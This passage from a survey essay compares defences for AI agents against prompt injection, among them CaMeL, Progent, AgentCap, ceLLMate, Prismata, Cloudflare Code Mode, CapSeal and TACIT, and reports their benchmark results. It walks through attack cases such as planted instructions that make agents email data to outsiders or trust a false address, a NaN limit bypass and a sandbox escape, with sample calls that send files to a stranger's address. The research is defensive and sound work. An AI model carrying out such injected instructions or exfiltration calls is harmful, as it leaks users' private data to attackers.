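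CaMeLoT can also enforce rules about the order of actions, which are awkward to write as a check on a single tool call. For example, a company may require human approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. In a test with seven deliberately faulty programs, CaMeLoT caught all seven and a simplified CaMeL caught one, but Nikolaou and colleagues had chosen the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express.

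Earlier checks save money but don't make the policies less strict. Of 97 AgentDojo tasks with no attack, both systems blocked the same 17. They disagreed on another 16, mostly because CaMeL blocked some programs over facts known only at run time.

### When one agent instructs another

In larger systems, one agent often delegates parts of a task to others. Peters-Gill and colleagues built such a system from three agents, each with its own CaMeL, and asked it to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. They had planted an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outside address.

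The database agent and the coordinating agent both treated the database text as untrusted data. But the coordinator's program inserted the summary into a sentence, "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", and passed the whole text to a third agent, which treated it as its user's request. The third agent's planner read the planted instruction and added a step to email the attacker. No agent had broken its own rules, but the text lost its "untrusted" label when it moved between them.

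Multi-CaMeL gives each call between agents two fields, one for instructions and one for data. The interpreter rejects an instruction that depends on anything a tool returned. The receiving planner sees only the names of the data values, and the values keep their tags. StruQ also used two fields, but a single model read both.

On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and never with multi-CaMeL. These are averages over five models, and most of the successful attacks were against two older ones. No attack on GPT-5.5 succeeded, even without any protection. On AssetOpsBench, multi-CaMeL's task completion rate was 3.2 percentage points lower than that of separate CaMeL agents.

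### When the user asks the agent to follow a document

In all of these designs, the steps come from the user's request, and other people's text supplies only details. Some requests don't fit this assumption. Chang and colleagues give the example of a document containing the sentence "Send the completed report to the address below." The sentence is just content if the user wants a summary, but it is a legitimate command if the user has asked the agent to carry out the document's instructions, even though the text and its provenance label are the same in both cases.

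Suppose the user tells the assistant, "Do what Bob asks in his latest email." The planner can't read the email, so it doesn't know which tools the task needs. It could write this:

```
steps = ask_reader("List the steps Bob wants", email, list[Step])
for step in steps:
    tools[step.name](step.argument)
```

This short program runs whatever the email contains. The planner has used permitted parts to build something like `eval`, which Caja withheld from guest code. The reader still has no tools, but its answer now determines which tools the agent calls.

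Garby and colleagues saw this happen when they tested CaMeL without policies. One banking task asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. The planner wrote a loop with a branch for each available tool, so an attacker who controlled the file could choose which tools the agent called.

With the policies on, the interpreter would trace every argument to an untrusted email and block any sensitive action, including those Bob asked for. If the planner endorses the email's contents, Bob's requests go through, but so do an attacker's. Both successful attacks on Randori were of this type. The user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Removing `endorse` blocked the attack but also prevented the agent from paying any bill this way. The original CaMeL evaluation included a similar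 case, which its designers treated as outside the attacks they were trying to stop.

Programmers often give agents this kind of task. When an agent installs software, it normally follows the project's README, a file of instructions from its developers. *You Told Me to Do It* (2026) found that agents often obeyed malicious instructions in READMEs, wherever in the file they appeared. The agents also followed links to further instructions and carried those out.

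A more precise label could help with Bob's email. If the mail system verifies the sender, a policy can accept Bob's requests and reject those from a stranger using his name. But Bob may have pasted in someone else's text, and a README can have hundreds of contributors. Even if Bob wrote every word, the user may not have meant to approve everything he asks for.

An engineer can limit the damage by deciding beforehand which tools such a task may use and how much money it may spend. The agent can also show the user each payment before making it. But a user who asked the agent to pay a bill from a file may never have seen the correct account number, so they may approve the attacker's.

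## Permission checks on tool calls and web actions

CaMeL and its successors change how an agent plans. A less disruptive option is to leave the agent's reasoning unchanged and put a check between the agent and its tools. The model may still read the stranger's email, follow its instructions and try to forward the invoices, but ordinary software controls whether the email tool runs.

### Why permission to send email is not enough

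The simplest check is a list of the tools an agent may use. For the meeting notes, the list would contain the document search, the inbox search and the email tool. It prevents the assistant from deleting files, but not from forwarding invoices, because the user's own request needs the email tool too. The two calls differ only in their arguments:

```
send_email(to="bob@work.example", body=notes)
send_email(to="stranger@example.com", body=invoices)
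```

Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined the public source code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's payments toolkit. All three let a developer choose which tools or actions the agent gets, but by default none of them checks whether the agent may use a tool with the specific values in a call. If the agent calls a tool with a stranger's address instead of Bob's, the toolkit still runs the call because the address is well formed. Mellafe Zuvic calls this a confused-deputy failure.

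Mellafe Zuvic demonstrated the problem on a simulated payment system, using a LangChain tool that changes the account a merchant is paid into. When a fixed model output called the tool with an attacker's account, LangChain made the change. ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's own check, blocked the same call because the account wasn't on the operator's list of allowed accounts. ScopeGate also caps payments and rejects any tool that the policy doesn't mention.

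An early version of ScopeGate had a hole much like the ones in JavaScript sandboxes. It blocked a payment only if the amount was greater than the limit. NaN, the special value for "not a number", is never greater than anything, so a payment of NaN went through. The repaired version accepts only a finite number within the permitted range. None of 48 prepared attacks got past it, and neither did any of the 29 unauthorized calls from an attacking model that learned the reason for each refusal and had 40 rounds to adapt. These were small tests by the tool's developer, who also knew which accounts belonged on the list of permitted accounts.

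For the meeting notes, the operator could permit email only to the user's saved contacts. This would block email to the stranger, but also to Bob if his address appeared only in the inbox. Mellafe Zuvic holds that no entry on the list may come from a model's output, even indirectly, because text that corrupts the call could also corrupt the list.

### Progent's changing rules

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a model to write a tool-call policy for each task, because a single policy broad enough for every task would be too broad to stop attacks. Each rule names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

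In their example, the user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. A model writes the first policy from the user's request alone, which allows only a search for that email. In the email, Alice asks for a summary of recent emails to be posted to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes allowing three more tools. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the Slack rule to allow messages only to that user.

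One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to an attacker. The policy-writing model may follow it and propose a rule that permits the forwarding. But before any change takes effect, a solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, compares the old rules with the new ones. If the new rules allow nothing that the old ones blocked, Progent applies them automatically. Otherwise, the update needs approval, which the developer can leave to a person or to a fixed setting, such as refusing every expansion. On the AgentDojo benchmark, 6% of the updates needed approval.

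So without approval, the set of calls the agent can make can only shrink. This guarantee covers only permissions, and an attack can succeed without breaking it. Suppose the first policy for the meeting notes allows email to any address, because nobody has found Bob's yet. If the model then narrows the rule to the stranger's false address, the solver will correctly accept the change, and the notes will go to the stranger.

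Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on ASB. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that it doesn't address attacks on the agent's written answers. Such an attack, for example one that makes the assistant give the user a false summary, doesn't require a tool call.

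### A separate grant for each call

AgentCap adds a check on where a call's arguments came from. Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, give an example policy for bank transfers. Adapted to email, it might look like this:

```
grant send_email {
  action: write
  resource: "mail/outgoing"
  intent: [send_document]
  trust: >= 0.8
  requires: [search_documents]
  ttl: 30s
  budget: 1
  bound_params: [to]
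}
```

Before each call, the agent requests a grant from AgentCap and declares a purpose. If the request passes every check, AgentCap issues a signed token, which in this example allows one email within 30 seconds. A gateway in front of the tool verifies the token before forwarding the call. The declared purpose is weak evidence because the model supplies it, but it ties the token to a use that the policy permits. AgentCap also keeps a trust score for each agent. Under the default settings, an agent loses permission to change anything after two suspicious events and loses all permissions after three.

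The token can't be forged and covers one action on one resource, so it is closer to an object capability than CaMeL's tags are. An agent can pass some of its authority to a helper agent, but it can't grant a larger budget or a later expiry than its own. Unlike a JavaScript reference, the token works only for the agent and session it was issued to.

The last line of the policy deals with the false address. AgentCap records which values appeared in trusted sources, such as the user's request, and which appeared only in untrusted ones. It rejects the stranger's address because that address appeared only in an email. It rejects Bob's real address for the same reason, unless the policy's author has marked another source that contains it, such as the company directory, as trusted.

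Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap by running 949 AgentDojo attacks against GPT-4o and GPT-5.4. AgentCap cut the attack success rate from 45.6% to 5.1% with GPT-4o and from 33.2% to zero with GPT-5.4. It also lowered the task completion rate when there was no attack, by 3.1 and 7.2 percentage points respectively. On InjecAgent, a second benchmark, the attack success rate fell from 23.2% to 8.6% with GPT-4o and from 12.0% to zero with GPT-5.4. The attacks that still worked on GPT-4o targeted only the agent's answer, used an argument the policy didn't protect, or arrived through an unlabeled field.

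Agents also completed more AgentDojo tasks with AgentCap than with Progent when there was no attack (78.4% compared with 68.0%). Progent's generated rules often allowed only the values that the model had predicted. Suresh and Gao fixed AgentCap's policies before the test and included no rules against particular attacks. But they wrote the policies by hand from the descriptions of the tools and the user tasks, and the developer of a real assistant can't read users' requests in advance. Each result also comes from a single run.

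Hand-written rules can contain mistakes too. AgentCap's policy checker found a customer-service policy under which no agent could use the `delete_customer` permission, because one rule required a combination of permissions that another rule prohibited.

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) explains why a tool call needs a check when it is made, even if someone reviewed the tool at installation. Its example is two email add-ons with identical code. One add-on's written instructions tell the model to use a fixed template, while the other's tell it to copy a password into the message. A code review can't tell them apart, but a check just before the email is sent can examine its actual contents.

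PACE compares each call's effects with authority derived from the user's request and looks for paths by which untrusted or secret data could reach a dangerous action. It had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for lowest in 14 more, and its task completion rate was at most three percentage points below an undefended agent's. However, the proofs cover a different configuration from the one tested. The tested configuration can restore a call that the path check blocked, or repair a call and run it without rechecking it, so the proven guarantee doesn't always hold for it.

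### An attacker who knows about Progent

Most of these results come from attacks that predate the defence. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent against an attack designed for it. The injected text presented the malicious action as a harmless step that the user had already authorized, to get the policy-writing model to allow it. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both the agent and the policy writer. The table shows averages over three runs.

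| AgentDojo tasks | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average attack success rate | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Average utility under attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The adaptive attack did no better than the standard one, whereas such attacks had defeated most of the model-based defences that Nasr and colleagues tested. But this adaptive attack may have been weak. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that its gentler wording, meant to reassure the policy writer, also made the agent less likely to obey. The office tasks don't test Progent, because the small model ignored those injections even without a defence. The averages for banking and Slack alone are about 39%, 6% and 4%.

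The test covered only eight user tasks in each group and one style of attack. It didn't include attack text optimized using the model's weights, or attacks that reach their goal entirely through calls the policy already allows. Attacks through allowed calls seem especially promising for an attacker, since they don't depend on an error in Progent. Progent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

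### Clicks on a page with many authors

An agent that works through a web browser clicks and types instead of calling named tools such as `send_email`. A click at the same position may open a message on one page and delete it on another. The browser is usually logged in to the user's accounts, so the agent has ambient authority over all of them. The page it reads may mix the site's own buttons with reviews, comments and advertisements from strangers.

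Blocking particular clicks or addresses doesn't work well. In *CELLMATE*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) tried to stop an agent from navigating directly to Hacker News, but the agent searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

Their system, ceLLMate, instead checks the HTTP requests that the browser sends to websites. However the agent reaches the "buy" button, the purchase produces a request to place an order. The website's developers publish an "agent sitemap", which translates such requests into named actions such as `PlaceOrder`. They or another trusted party also write policies, for example one that allows an order up to a maximum price.

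When the user gives the agent a task, a language model selects the policies it needs and fills in details such as the price limit. The model sees only the request and the prepared policies, so a malicious product review can't influence it. Once the user confirms the selection, it stays fixed. A browser extension blocks requests that the policies don't allow. A $50 price limit alone would let the agent buy two $49 baskets, so a policy can also limit the number of orders.

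Meng and colleagues tested the selection step on 209 tasks for shopping, travel and software websites. Three leading models chose exactly the right policies at least 94% of the time in every category. They were less reliable on 32 shopping tasks that involved values such as a price limit, where they got both the policies and the values right 81% to 97% of the time.

To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues assumed that an attacker had already taken over the agent. They wrote 12 scripts that attempted malicious actions on GitLab, a site for software projects, such as deleting a project or creating an access token. ceLLMate blocked all 12, since the user's task was only to comment on an issue or upvote it. Pages took 7.25% to 15% longer to load, depending on the size of the sitemap.

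All of those attacks needed an action the policy didn't permit. ceLLMate doesn't check the contents of permitted comments, so a stranger could still try to make the agent post private information in one. It also depends on websites to publish accurate sitemaps. Meng and colleagues built their GitLab sitemap by hand, with entries for 51 functions.

*Prismata* (Villa, Tan and colleagues, 2026) doesn't require the website's cooperation. It relies on the structure of a web page, which is a tree of nested elements in which a section may contain a form and the form a button. For each button, link or field, a language model sees only the user's task and the chain of elements from the top of the page down to that item, and decides whether the task requires the item. A malicious review elsewhere on the page isn't in that chain, so it can't affect the decision about a password-reset button.

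Some chains pass through text written by outsiders, such as the one leading to a reply button inside a review. Prismata therefore also works down each chain one level at a time. If a heading or a developer's label such as "reviews" indicates that outsiders wrote what follows, Prismata marks everything below as untrusted before the model reads it. It removes this content if the task doesn't need it. Otherwise, it leaves the content readable but disables its buttons and links. Ordinary code filters the page before the agent sees it and rejects any click on a disabled item.

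Villa and colleagues examined 90,408 pieces of content from outsiders on 5,664 pages. Only 1,086 contained anything clickable, and a warning label preceded all but 94 of those. Of the 94, 79 were ordinary links, and following a link shouldn't change anything on a well-built site. The exceptions are rare on average, but an attacker can look for a site that has one.

In the main test, an agent running on GPT-5.4-mini worked on websites modeled on real ones, with pop-ups designed to get it to click. Prismata reduced the attack success rate from 85.5% to 0.7%, averaged over three types of pop-up and three runs. Under attack, the agent completed 23.0% of its tasks with Prismata and 4.5% without it. When there was no attack, it completed 26.6% with Prismata and 29.9% without it. Adaptive versions of the pop-ups, tried on 20 tasks, succeeded 65% to 100% of the time without Prismata and never with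 it.

This defence is well suited to pop-ups because few tasks require the agent to click on an advertisement. If the assistant used a webmail page to send the meeting notes, Prismata could disable the settings and make the emails read-only, but the agent would still have to read them to find Bob's address. It could then type the stranger's address into the "To" field, which the task needs. Villa and colleagues exclude attacks like this, which use only the permissions the task requires. Prismata also doesn't cover instructions hidden in images. Its extra model calls raised the cost of a 20-task run from $1.11 to $1.62, even though it reused many earlier answers.

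### Who can write the policy

Policies are hardest to write when nobody knows the steps in advance. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, found that only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks required an agent to revise its plan as it learned more. They built a benchmark of 60 tasks in which the agent always has to do so, with 560 combinations of task and attack. Each task also includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a notice on a checkout page to log in first, so a defence can't succeed by ignoring all outside instructions. These are some of the results with GPT-4o:

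| Defence | Utility without an attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| Spotlighting | 55.0% | 27.6% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Progent's utility ranged from 3.3% to 25.0% across four models. With more than 30 tools available, its policy-writing model often assigned the wrong permissions. The errors accumulated over a long task until Progent had blocked almost every useful tool. *DRIFT* (2025) describes a design that also updates its rules during the task, but adds a second check when the agent departs from the original plan. This design did better, but three of its designers also worked on AgentDyn.

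The models in this comparison were fairly old, and the attacks were simple. The researchers also told the agents to finish every task without asking the user for confirmation, because agents that stopped to ask scored badly. Some of the blocked work might have gone ahead if a person had been available to approve it.

A good policy for such tasks has to let outside text supply details without letting it add new goals. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) illustrates this with a request to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. A search result may supply the report's file number, because the user has already authorized sending that report. If the same result contains an instruction to send a copy to someone else, following it would exceed what the user authorized. SARA, the system built on this distinction, kept attack success rates at or below 0.63% in its four main tests, which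 included AgentDyn. But it has to determine what the user's request covers, and it can get this wrong.

Developers can partly separate trusted from untrusted text in advance by deciding which fields of a tool call outside text may fill. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) gives the example of an error log from a software project. The agent may take the path of the file to repair from the log, once trusted code has checked that the path is valid, but nothing in the log can mark the repair as approved. The policy's author must classify every field of every tool that can change something, and the system rejects any unclassified field. In 400 test tasks on software projects, no unauthorized action got through, and the agent safely completed 231 of them.

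The developers of a tool or website know what each field does, but not what a particular user wants. Meng and colleagues expect websites to write agent sitemaps because they already write Content Security Policies. That precedent is discouraging, since Weichselbaum and colleagues found almost all such policies easy to bypass. Users know what they want, but they may not know whether a request for another tool is reasonable, and may approve it just to get the task done.

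A model can write a permission policy based on both the user's request and the available tools, but the policy is only a draft and needs review, as LavaMoat's generated policies do. An assistant needs a new policy for every request, while a LavaMoat policy lasts until the next dependency update. If the request is to send an email, reviewing the full policy could take longer than sending the email by hand.

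Permission checks are easier to write for repeated tasks. If a company's agent pays invoices every day, its accountants can keep a list of suppliers and their account numbers, and checking each payment against that list will stop most false invoices. Nobody can write such a list beforehand for a request like "do what Bob asks in his latest email", so a person will probably have to approve each new recipient or payment as it comes up.

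## Agents that write code for a capability sandbox

A policy on tool calls has to check each call separately, after the model has chosen it. Engineers can instead have the model write a program, and decide beforehand which objects that program can reach. The program is then a guest, like the weather widget in the webmail page, except that the model has just written it for a single task. CaMeL's planner also writes programs, but it must write them before the agent reads any outside text. The designs in this section have no such rule, so the model can read a program's output and then write another.

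### Tools as a programming interface

Many agents use external tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way for a service to describe its tools to any agent. For each call, the model writes a short structured message, ordinary software runs the tool, and the result goes back into the model's input. The model has to read every result, even one it only copies into the next call.

Code Mode, which the internet infrastructure company Cloudflare introduced in September 2025, works differently. Varda and Pai, in *Code Mode*, explain that software turns the descriptions of the tools into an interface in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with declared types. The model sees this interface and gets just one tool, which runs code. A program might look like this one, adapted from the documentation, Cloudflare's *Codemode*:

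```
async () => {
  const forecast = await codemode.getWeather({ location: "Oslo" });
  if (forecast.includes("rain")) {
    await codemode.sendEmail({
      to: "bob@work.example",
      subject: "Bring an umbrella",
      body: forecast,
    });
  }
};
```

Cloudflare runs each program in a new isolate, a separate instance of Google's V8 engine, and discards the isolate afterwards. Inside it, the usual functions for reaching the internet, `fetch` and `connect`, throw errors. The `codemode` object is a Proxy that sends each call to the host, which runs the real tool and returns the result. The program can call only the tools that the host has supplied.

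Varda and Pai call the live objects that connect an isolate to a service "bindings". On most platforms, a program uses general network access and a secret key to reach a private service. A binding replaces both and works like an object capability. The host keeps the key and adds it to each outgoing request, so the program has no key to leak.

The host can also limit a binding to the functions it wants to allow, even if the service behind it can do more. *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* argues that this is easier than filtering web requests, which is ceLLMate's approach, because a filter has to work out what each request would do, including the effects of its headers and parameters. In its example, a program that holds only a chat room object can read past messages, subscribe to new ones and post, but can't delete the room.

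The isolate is a weaker boundary than a virtual machine. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in the software that runs virtual machines. Cloudflare therefore installs V8's security fixes within hours, puts a second sandbox around the isolates, and separates customers according to risk. It has also added defences against Spectre, which matter here because a new isolate often runs on the same thread as the program that created it.

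Those protections come with Cloudflare's service. Developers can also connect Code Mode to another sandbox. The documentation suggests Node's `vm` as one option, but guest code can escape `vm` by following constructors.

### Fewer tokens, same authority

An agent can use fewer tokens by writing one program instead of reading every intermediate result. Varda and colleagues report that turning a set of tools into a TypeScript interface can cut token use by 81%. The saving doesn't depend on how safely the program runs, so an agent that used Node's `vm` would save as many tokens as one that used Cloudflare's isolates.

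Carey's *Code Mode*, a later post with the same short title, describes a much larger reduction in tokens. Cloudflare's customers control its services through an interface with more than 2,500 operations, and describing each one as a tool would take 1.17 million tokens. Cloudflare instead gives the model two tools that take about 1,000 tokens. The model uses one to search the operations' descriptions with code and the other to run programs that carry out the operations.

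The second tool gives each program a function, `cloudflare.request()`, which can call any operation in the interface. The isolate keeps the program away from the rest of the internet, but it wouldn't stop a misled model from changing the customer's firewall. The access token limits what the program can do, because it carries only the permissions the user approved when connecting the agent. If the user approves every permission, the tool still saves as many model tokens, but the user gets much less protection.

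Writing programs has one security benefit, for the same reason it produces the savings. If a program passes an email's text directly from one tool to another, the model never reads it, so instructions in the email can't change what the model does next. But most tasks require the model to read something, and whatever the program returns goes into the model's input.

Cloudflare's posts on Code Mode give token counts and start-up times but no attack success rate. The best evidence that Code Mode is practical comes from Zite, whose users build apps by chatting with a model. Zite runs the generated code in Dynamic Workers, the Cloudflare feature that creates isolates on demand, and handles millions of execution requests a day. Each automation can access only the services and libraries it needs. Cloudflare opened Dynamic Workers to all paying Workers customers in March (*Dynamic Workers, now in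 open beta*, 2026). In August, it released Cloudflare OS, an open-source platform on which staff can build apps and automate their work. InfoQ's *Cloudflare OS* (2026) describes the platform as built on a capability-based model.

### Using a key without holding it

Many agents still get their keys in files or settings that the model can read and repeat. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) instead puts the keys in a broker, a trusted program on the same computer. The agent asks the broker for a handle that allows one narrow kind of action, such as sending data in a fixed format to one web address. When the agent uses the handle, the broker checks the request, adds the key, sends the request and removes any credentials from the response.

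CapSeal also covers SSH, a system for running commands on remote computers. Many developers let a program use their SSH keys through a forwarding connection, which would give an agent broad power even if it never saw the keys. CapSeal's broker instead checks the remote computer's identity and then runs the approved command itself.

Jin and colleagues tested CapSeal against two systems that gave the agent its keys directly. When prompts tried to extract a key for a web service, both other systems leaked it in every trial and CapSeal never did. None of the three systems leaked an SSH key. CapSeal's agent could hardly have revealed a key it never received, but the test is still a useful check of the software.

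Jin and colleagues also tried to make the agents use their keys for forbidden addresses or commands. No attempt succeeded against any system, including the two without CapSeal, so the test provides no evidence that CapSeal prevents such misuse. The broker added about 0.15 milliseconds to a typical web request and 0.21 milliseconds to an SSH command.

A misled agent can still use a key that is hidden from it. If a handle lets the agent send email through a mail service, a stranger who influences the agent can get it to send an email, and the broker will add the key to the request.

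### From one document to a read-only directory

Cloudflare's bindings usually represent whole services. The Endo Familiar, a prototype that developers of Hardened JavaScript demonstrated in April 2026, applies the same idea to individual files. In the demonstration, an agent first has access to one document, then to a directory, and finally to a read-only view of that directory.

An agent that is given only today's meeting notes can't reach the user's invoices. Giving the agent a whole directory saves the user from picking each file, but the agent also gets power over everything inside, including files the user adds later. With a read-only view of the directory, the agent can still look through the files but can't change or delete them.

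A read-only directory is harder to write than a read-only file. In Hardened JavaScript, it might look like this, where `readOnly` is the earlier wrapper that exposes only a file's `read` function:

```
function readOnlyDirectory(dir) {
  return harden({
    list: () => dir.list(),
    open: (name) => readOnly(dir.open(name)),
  });
}
```

If `open` returned the original file, the agent could open a document through the read-only directory and then overwrite it. A full version would also have to wrap subdirectories. `dir.open` must reject names such as `../invoices`, which on most systems lead to a neighbouring directory. An object-capability directory avoids this problem because it holds references only to its own contents, so no name leads out of it.

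The Familiar makes this mechanism easy to follow, and wallets already use Hardened JavaScript. But the demonstration doesn't measure how often attacks succeed or how many tasks an agent completes.

### Planning to take a capability back

Kris Kowal, one of the developers of SES, warns that agents may pass their capabilities on, so anyone who grants a capability must plan how to revoke it. For example, an assistant might ask a helper agent to summarize the files in a directory and pass along its own reference to that directory. JavaScript doesn't list who holds a reference, and the host can't remove one from the helper's memory.

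The host can keep control by giving out a view that it can switch off:

```
function revocable(dir) {
  let target = dir;
  return {
    view: harden({
      list: () => target.list(),
      read: (name) => target.open(name).read(),
    }),
    revoke: () => { target = undefined; },
  };
}
```

The host gives `view` to the assistant and keeps `revoke`. Once the host calls `revoke()`, `view` stops working for the assistant, the helper and anyone else who received it. The host has to set this up before granting access, because it can't insert a wrapper between an agent and a directory that the agent already holds.

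This view has a `read` function that returns plain text, whereas the earlier view had `open`. If `read` returned file objects, an agent could open every file and keep using those objects after the host revoked the directory. To share live objects, the host needs a membrane that simultaneously disables everything reached through the view. Neither version can take back text that an agent has already read.

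A single switch also revokes everyone's access at once. If the assistant makes a second revocable view for the helper, it can end the helper's access as soon as the summary is ready and keep using the directory. But a model may not take these steps, so the surrounding software may need to do them automatically.

Some designs avoid the problem by preventing agents from passing on a working capability. CapSeal's handles are useless outside the session that received them, and the broker can revoke them. Cloudflare's *Agents SDK improves browser automation, code execution, and recovery* (2026) describes another approach. A parent agent can offer its tools to a helper, but each of the helper's calls goes back to a function in the parent, which runs the tool. A developer can make that function refuse further calls at any time.

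### Capabilities that a compiler tracks

Wrappers like these control what a program can do while it runs, but a compiler can catch some violations before it starts. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) have agents write programs in Scala 3, which has an experimental feature that tracks capabilities. Their system, TACIT, compiles each program in a restricted mode and runs it only if the compiler accepts it.

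The compiler records which capabilities a value can use as part of the value's type. Suppose `f` is a file, and a function takes a string and writes it to `f`. The function has the type

`String ->{f} Unit`

where the braces list the capabilities it uses and `Unit` means that it returns nothing useful. A function of type `String -> String`, without braces, is pure. It can turn one string into another but can't write to a file, send a message or have any other effect outside itself.

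TACIT uses this distinction to protect secrets. When a program reads a protected file, it gets the contents in a container called `Classified`, and it can work on them only by passing a pure function to the container's `map` function:

```
val notes = readClassified("notes.txt")
notes.map(text => text.toUpperCase)          // accepted
notes.map(text => { f.write(text); text })   // rejected
```

The first call returns the capitalized text in another `Classified` container. If the program prints this container, the user sees the text, but the agent's model receives only `Classified(****)`. To get a summary, the program can send the container to a separate, trusted model that has no tools. The model's answer is also `Classified`. This second model is the reader in the dual-model pattern, and the compiler prevents the agent's program from unwrapping the answer.

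A conventional sandbox can't provide this protection just by limiting which files and services a program may use. Odersky and colleagues give the example of an agent that may read a private file and call a model in the cloud. Both operations are legitimate, but the agent leaks data if it passes the file's contents to the model. Cloudflare's isolate would have the same weakness if the host supplied bindings for both operations.

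Scala's types also limit how long a capability lasts. A TACIT program can access files only within one block of code. If the block returns a function that would read a file later, the function's type includes that file access, and the compiler rejects the program. The host therefore doesn't have to revoke the access itself. Odersky and colleagues suggest using the same method for delegation, with the compiler rejecting any helper program that needs more than the helper's share of capabilities, but they haven't evaluated this. *LACUNA* (2026) uses the Scala feature for programs with holes that an agent fills with code. That code can use only the capabilities available where the hole is.

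All this depends on a trusted library that connects the programs to real files and services. Its developers can mark code as safe without the compiler checking it, so a mistake there could leak data, as a mistake in Caja's host objects could. The compiler also can't track what outside programs such as `git` do, and it doesn't prevent leaks through timing.

### Testing the Scala harness

To test whether TACIT prevents leaks, Odersky and colleagues hid keys and confidential documents in a software project. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with ten prompt injections, and added 11 requests in which the user tried to obtain the secrets. The table shows how many trials leaked a secret.

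| Model | Attack | Plain text | `Classified` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Prompt injection | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Malicious user | 2 of 11 | 0 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Prompt injection | 3 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Malicious user | 8 of 11 | 0 of 11 |

`Classified` prevented every leak in the test, but only three of the 13 leaks without it came from prompt injection. The test is therefore better evidence that `Classified` protects against malicious users than that it protects against prompt injection. The test also counted a secret as leaked only if it appeared in the agent's output.

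Protection didn't reduce the number of ordinary tasks the agents completed. Under injection, MiniMax completed 90.0% with `Classified` and 88.3% without it. Sonnet completed 99.2% with it and 83.3% without it, but Odersky and colleagues suspect that their setup caused some of the difference. Without the protection, Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo with two older models. Only one of 1,926 attacks counted as successful, and in that case the agent booked the correct hotel but quoted a review recommending the attacker's. But they didn't run the same agents without TACIT, so it is unclear how many attacks the models would have resisted anyway.

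With o4-mini-high, TACIT did worse than CaMeL in all four groups of AgentDojo tasks, and completed 52.9% of the office tasks compared with CaMeL's 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT was slightly ahead in banking and behind in office work and Slack, but it completed 64.3% of the travel tasks and CaMeL only 1.4%. Odersky and colleagues describe the two systems' task completion as comparable, which is generous to TACIT given the o4-mini-high results.

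Writing Scala didn't make agents much worse at ordinary work. On τ²-bench, a simulation of customer service, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala than when they called tools directly. At most 8% of the programs in these tests failed to compile and needed another attempt. On SWE-bench Lite, where agents repair real software bugs, MiniMax solved 41.7% of the problems with Scala and 43.3% without it.

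### The meeting notes in Code Mode

None of these tests covers an agent that sends the right document to the wrong person. Suppose the email assistant uses Code Mode and has tools to find documents, search the inbox and send email. To find Bob's address, the model first writes this program:

```
async () => {
  return await codemode.searchInbox({ query: "Bob" });
};
```

The result goes into the model's input. It includes the stranger's email, which begins "Hi, Bob here" and gives a false address. The model believes it and writes a second program:

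```
async () => {
  const notes = await codemode.findDocument({
    title: "Today's meeting notes",
  });
  await codemode.sendEmail({
    to: "stranger@example.com",
    subject: "Meeting notes",
    body: notes.text,
  });
};
```

The isolate runs the program correctly. The program uses only the objects that the host supplied, never connects to the network directly and never has access to the mail service's key, but the stranger still gets the notes.

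If the model had instead obeyed the stranger's instruction about invoices, it could have searched for the invoices and sent them in the same way. The host can prevent that by supplying only the meeting notes, as in the first step of the Familiar's demonstration, but the program could still send the notes to anyone. Writing a single program before the model reads the inbox isn't enough either. If that program takes the address from the newest email that mentions Bob, it will use the stranger's address.

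TACIT could block the second program if the notes were `Classified` and its email function accepted only ordinary text. But then the compiler would also reject the program with Bob's real address. The library's developers could add an email function that accepts classified text for approved recipients, but somebody would still have to approve Bob's address. If the notes were ordinary text, the second program would compile and send them to the stranger.

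Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that hostile text can still influence the agent, and promise only that it can't make the agent's code exceed its capabilities. They argue that any harmful injection must either send private data to an unauthorized destination or use a capability that the agent wasn't given. That seems too narrow, since an agent with permission to edit a directory can do serious harm by deleting the files in it. In the meeting notes example, the destination is unauthorized only because the user meant a different person, and the program's types don't record whom the user meant.

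Since June 2026, Code Mode has been able to pause at actions that need approval. Before then, it left out tools that needed approval. If the host requires approval for `sendEmail`, the second program stops before the email goes out. Once the user approves, Code Mode replays the results of the calls it has already made, sends the email and continues the program. As with CapLite's requests for confirmation, this helps only if the user notices the false address.

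## What carries over from JavaScript to agents and what does not

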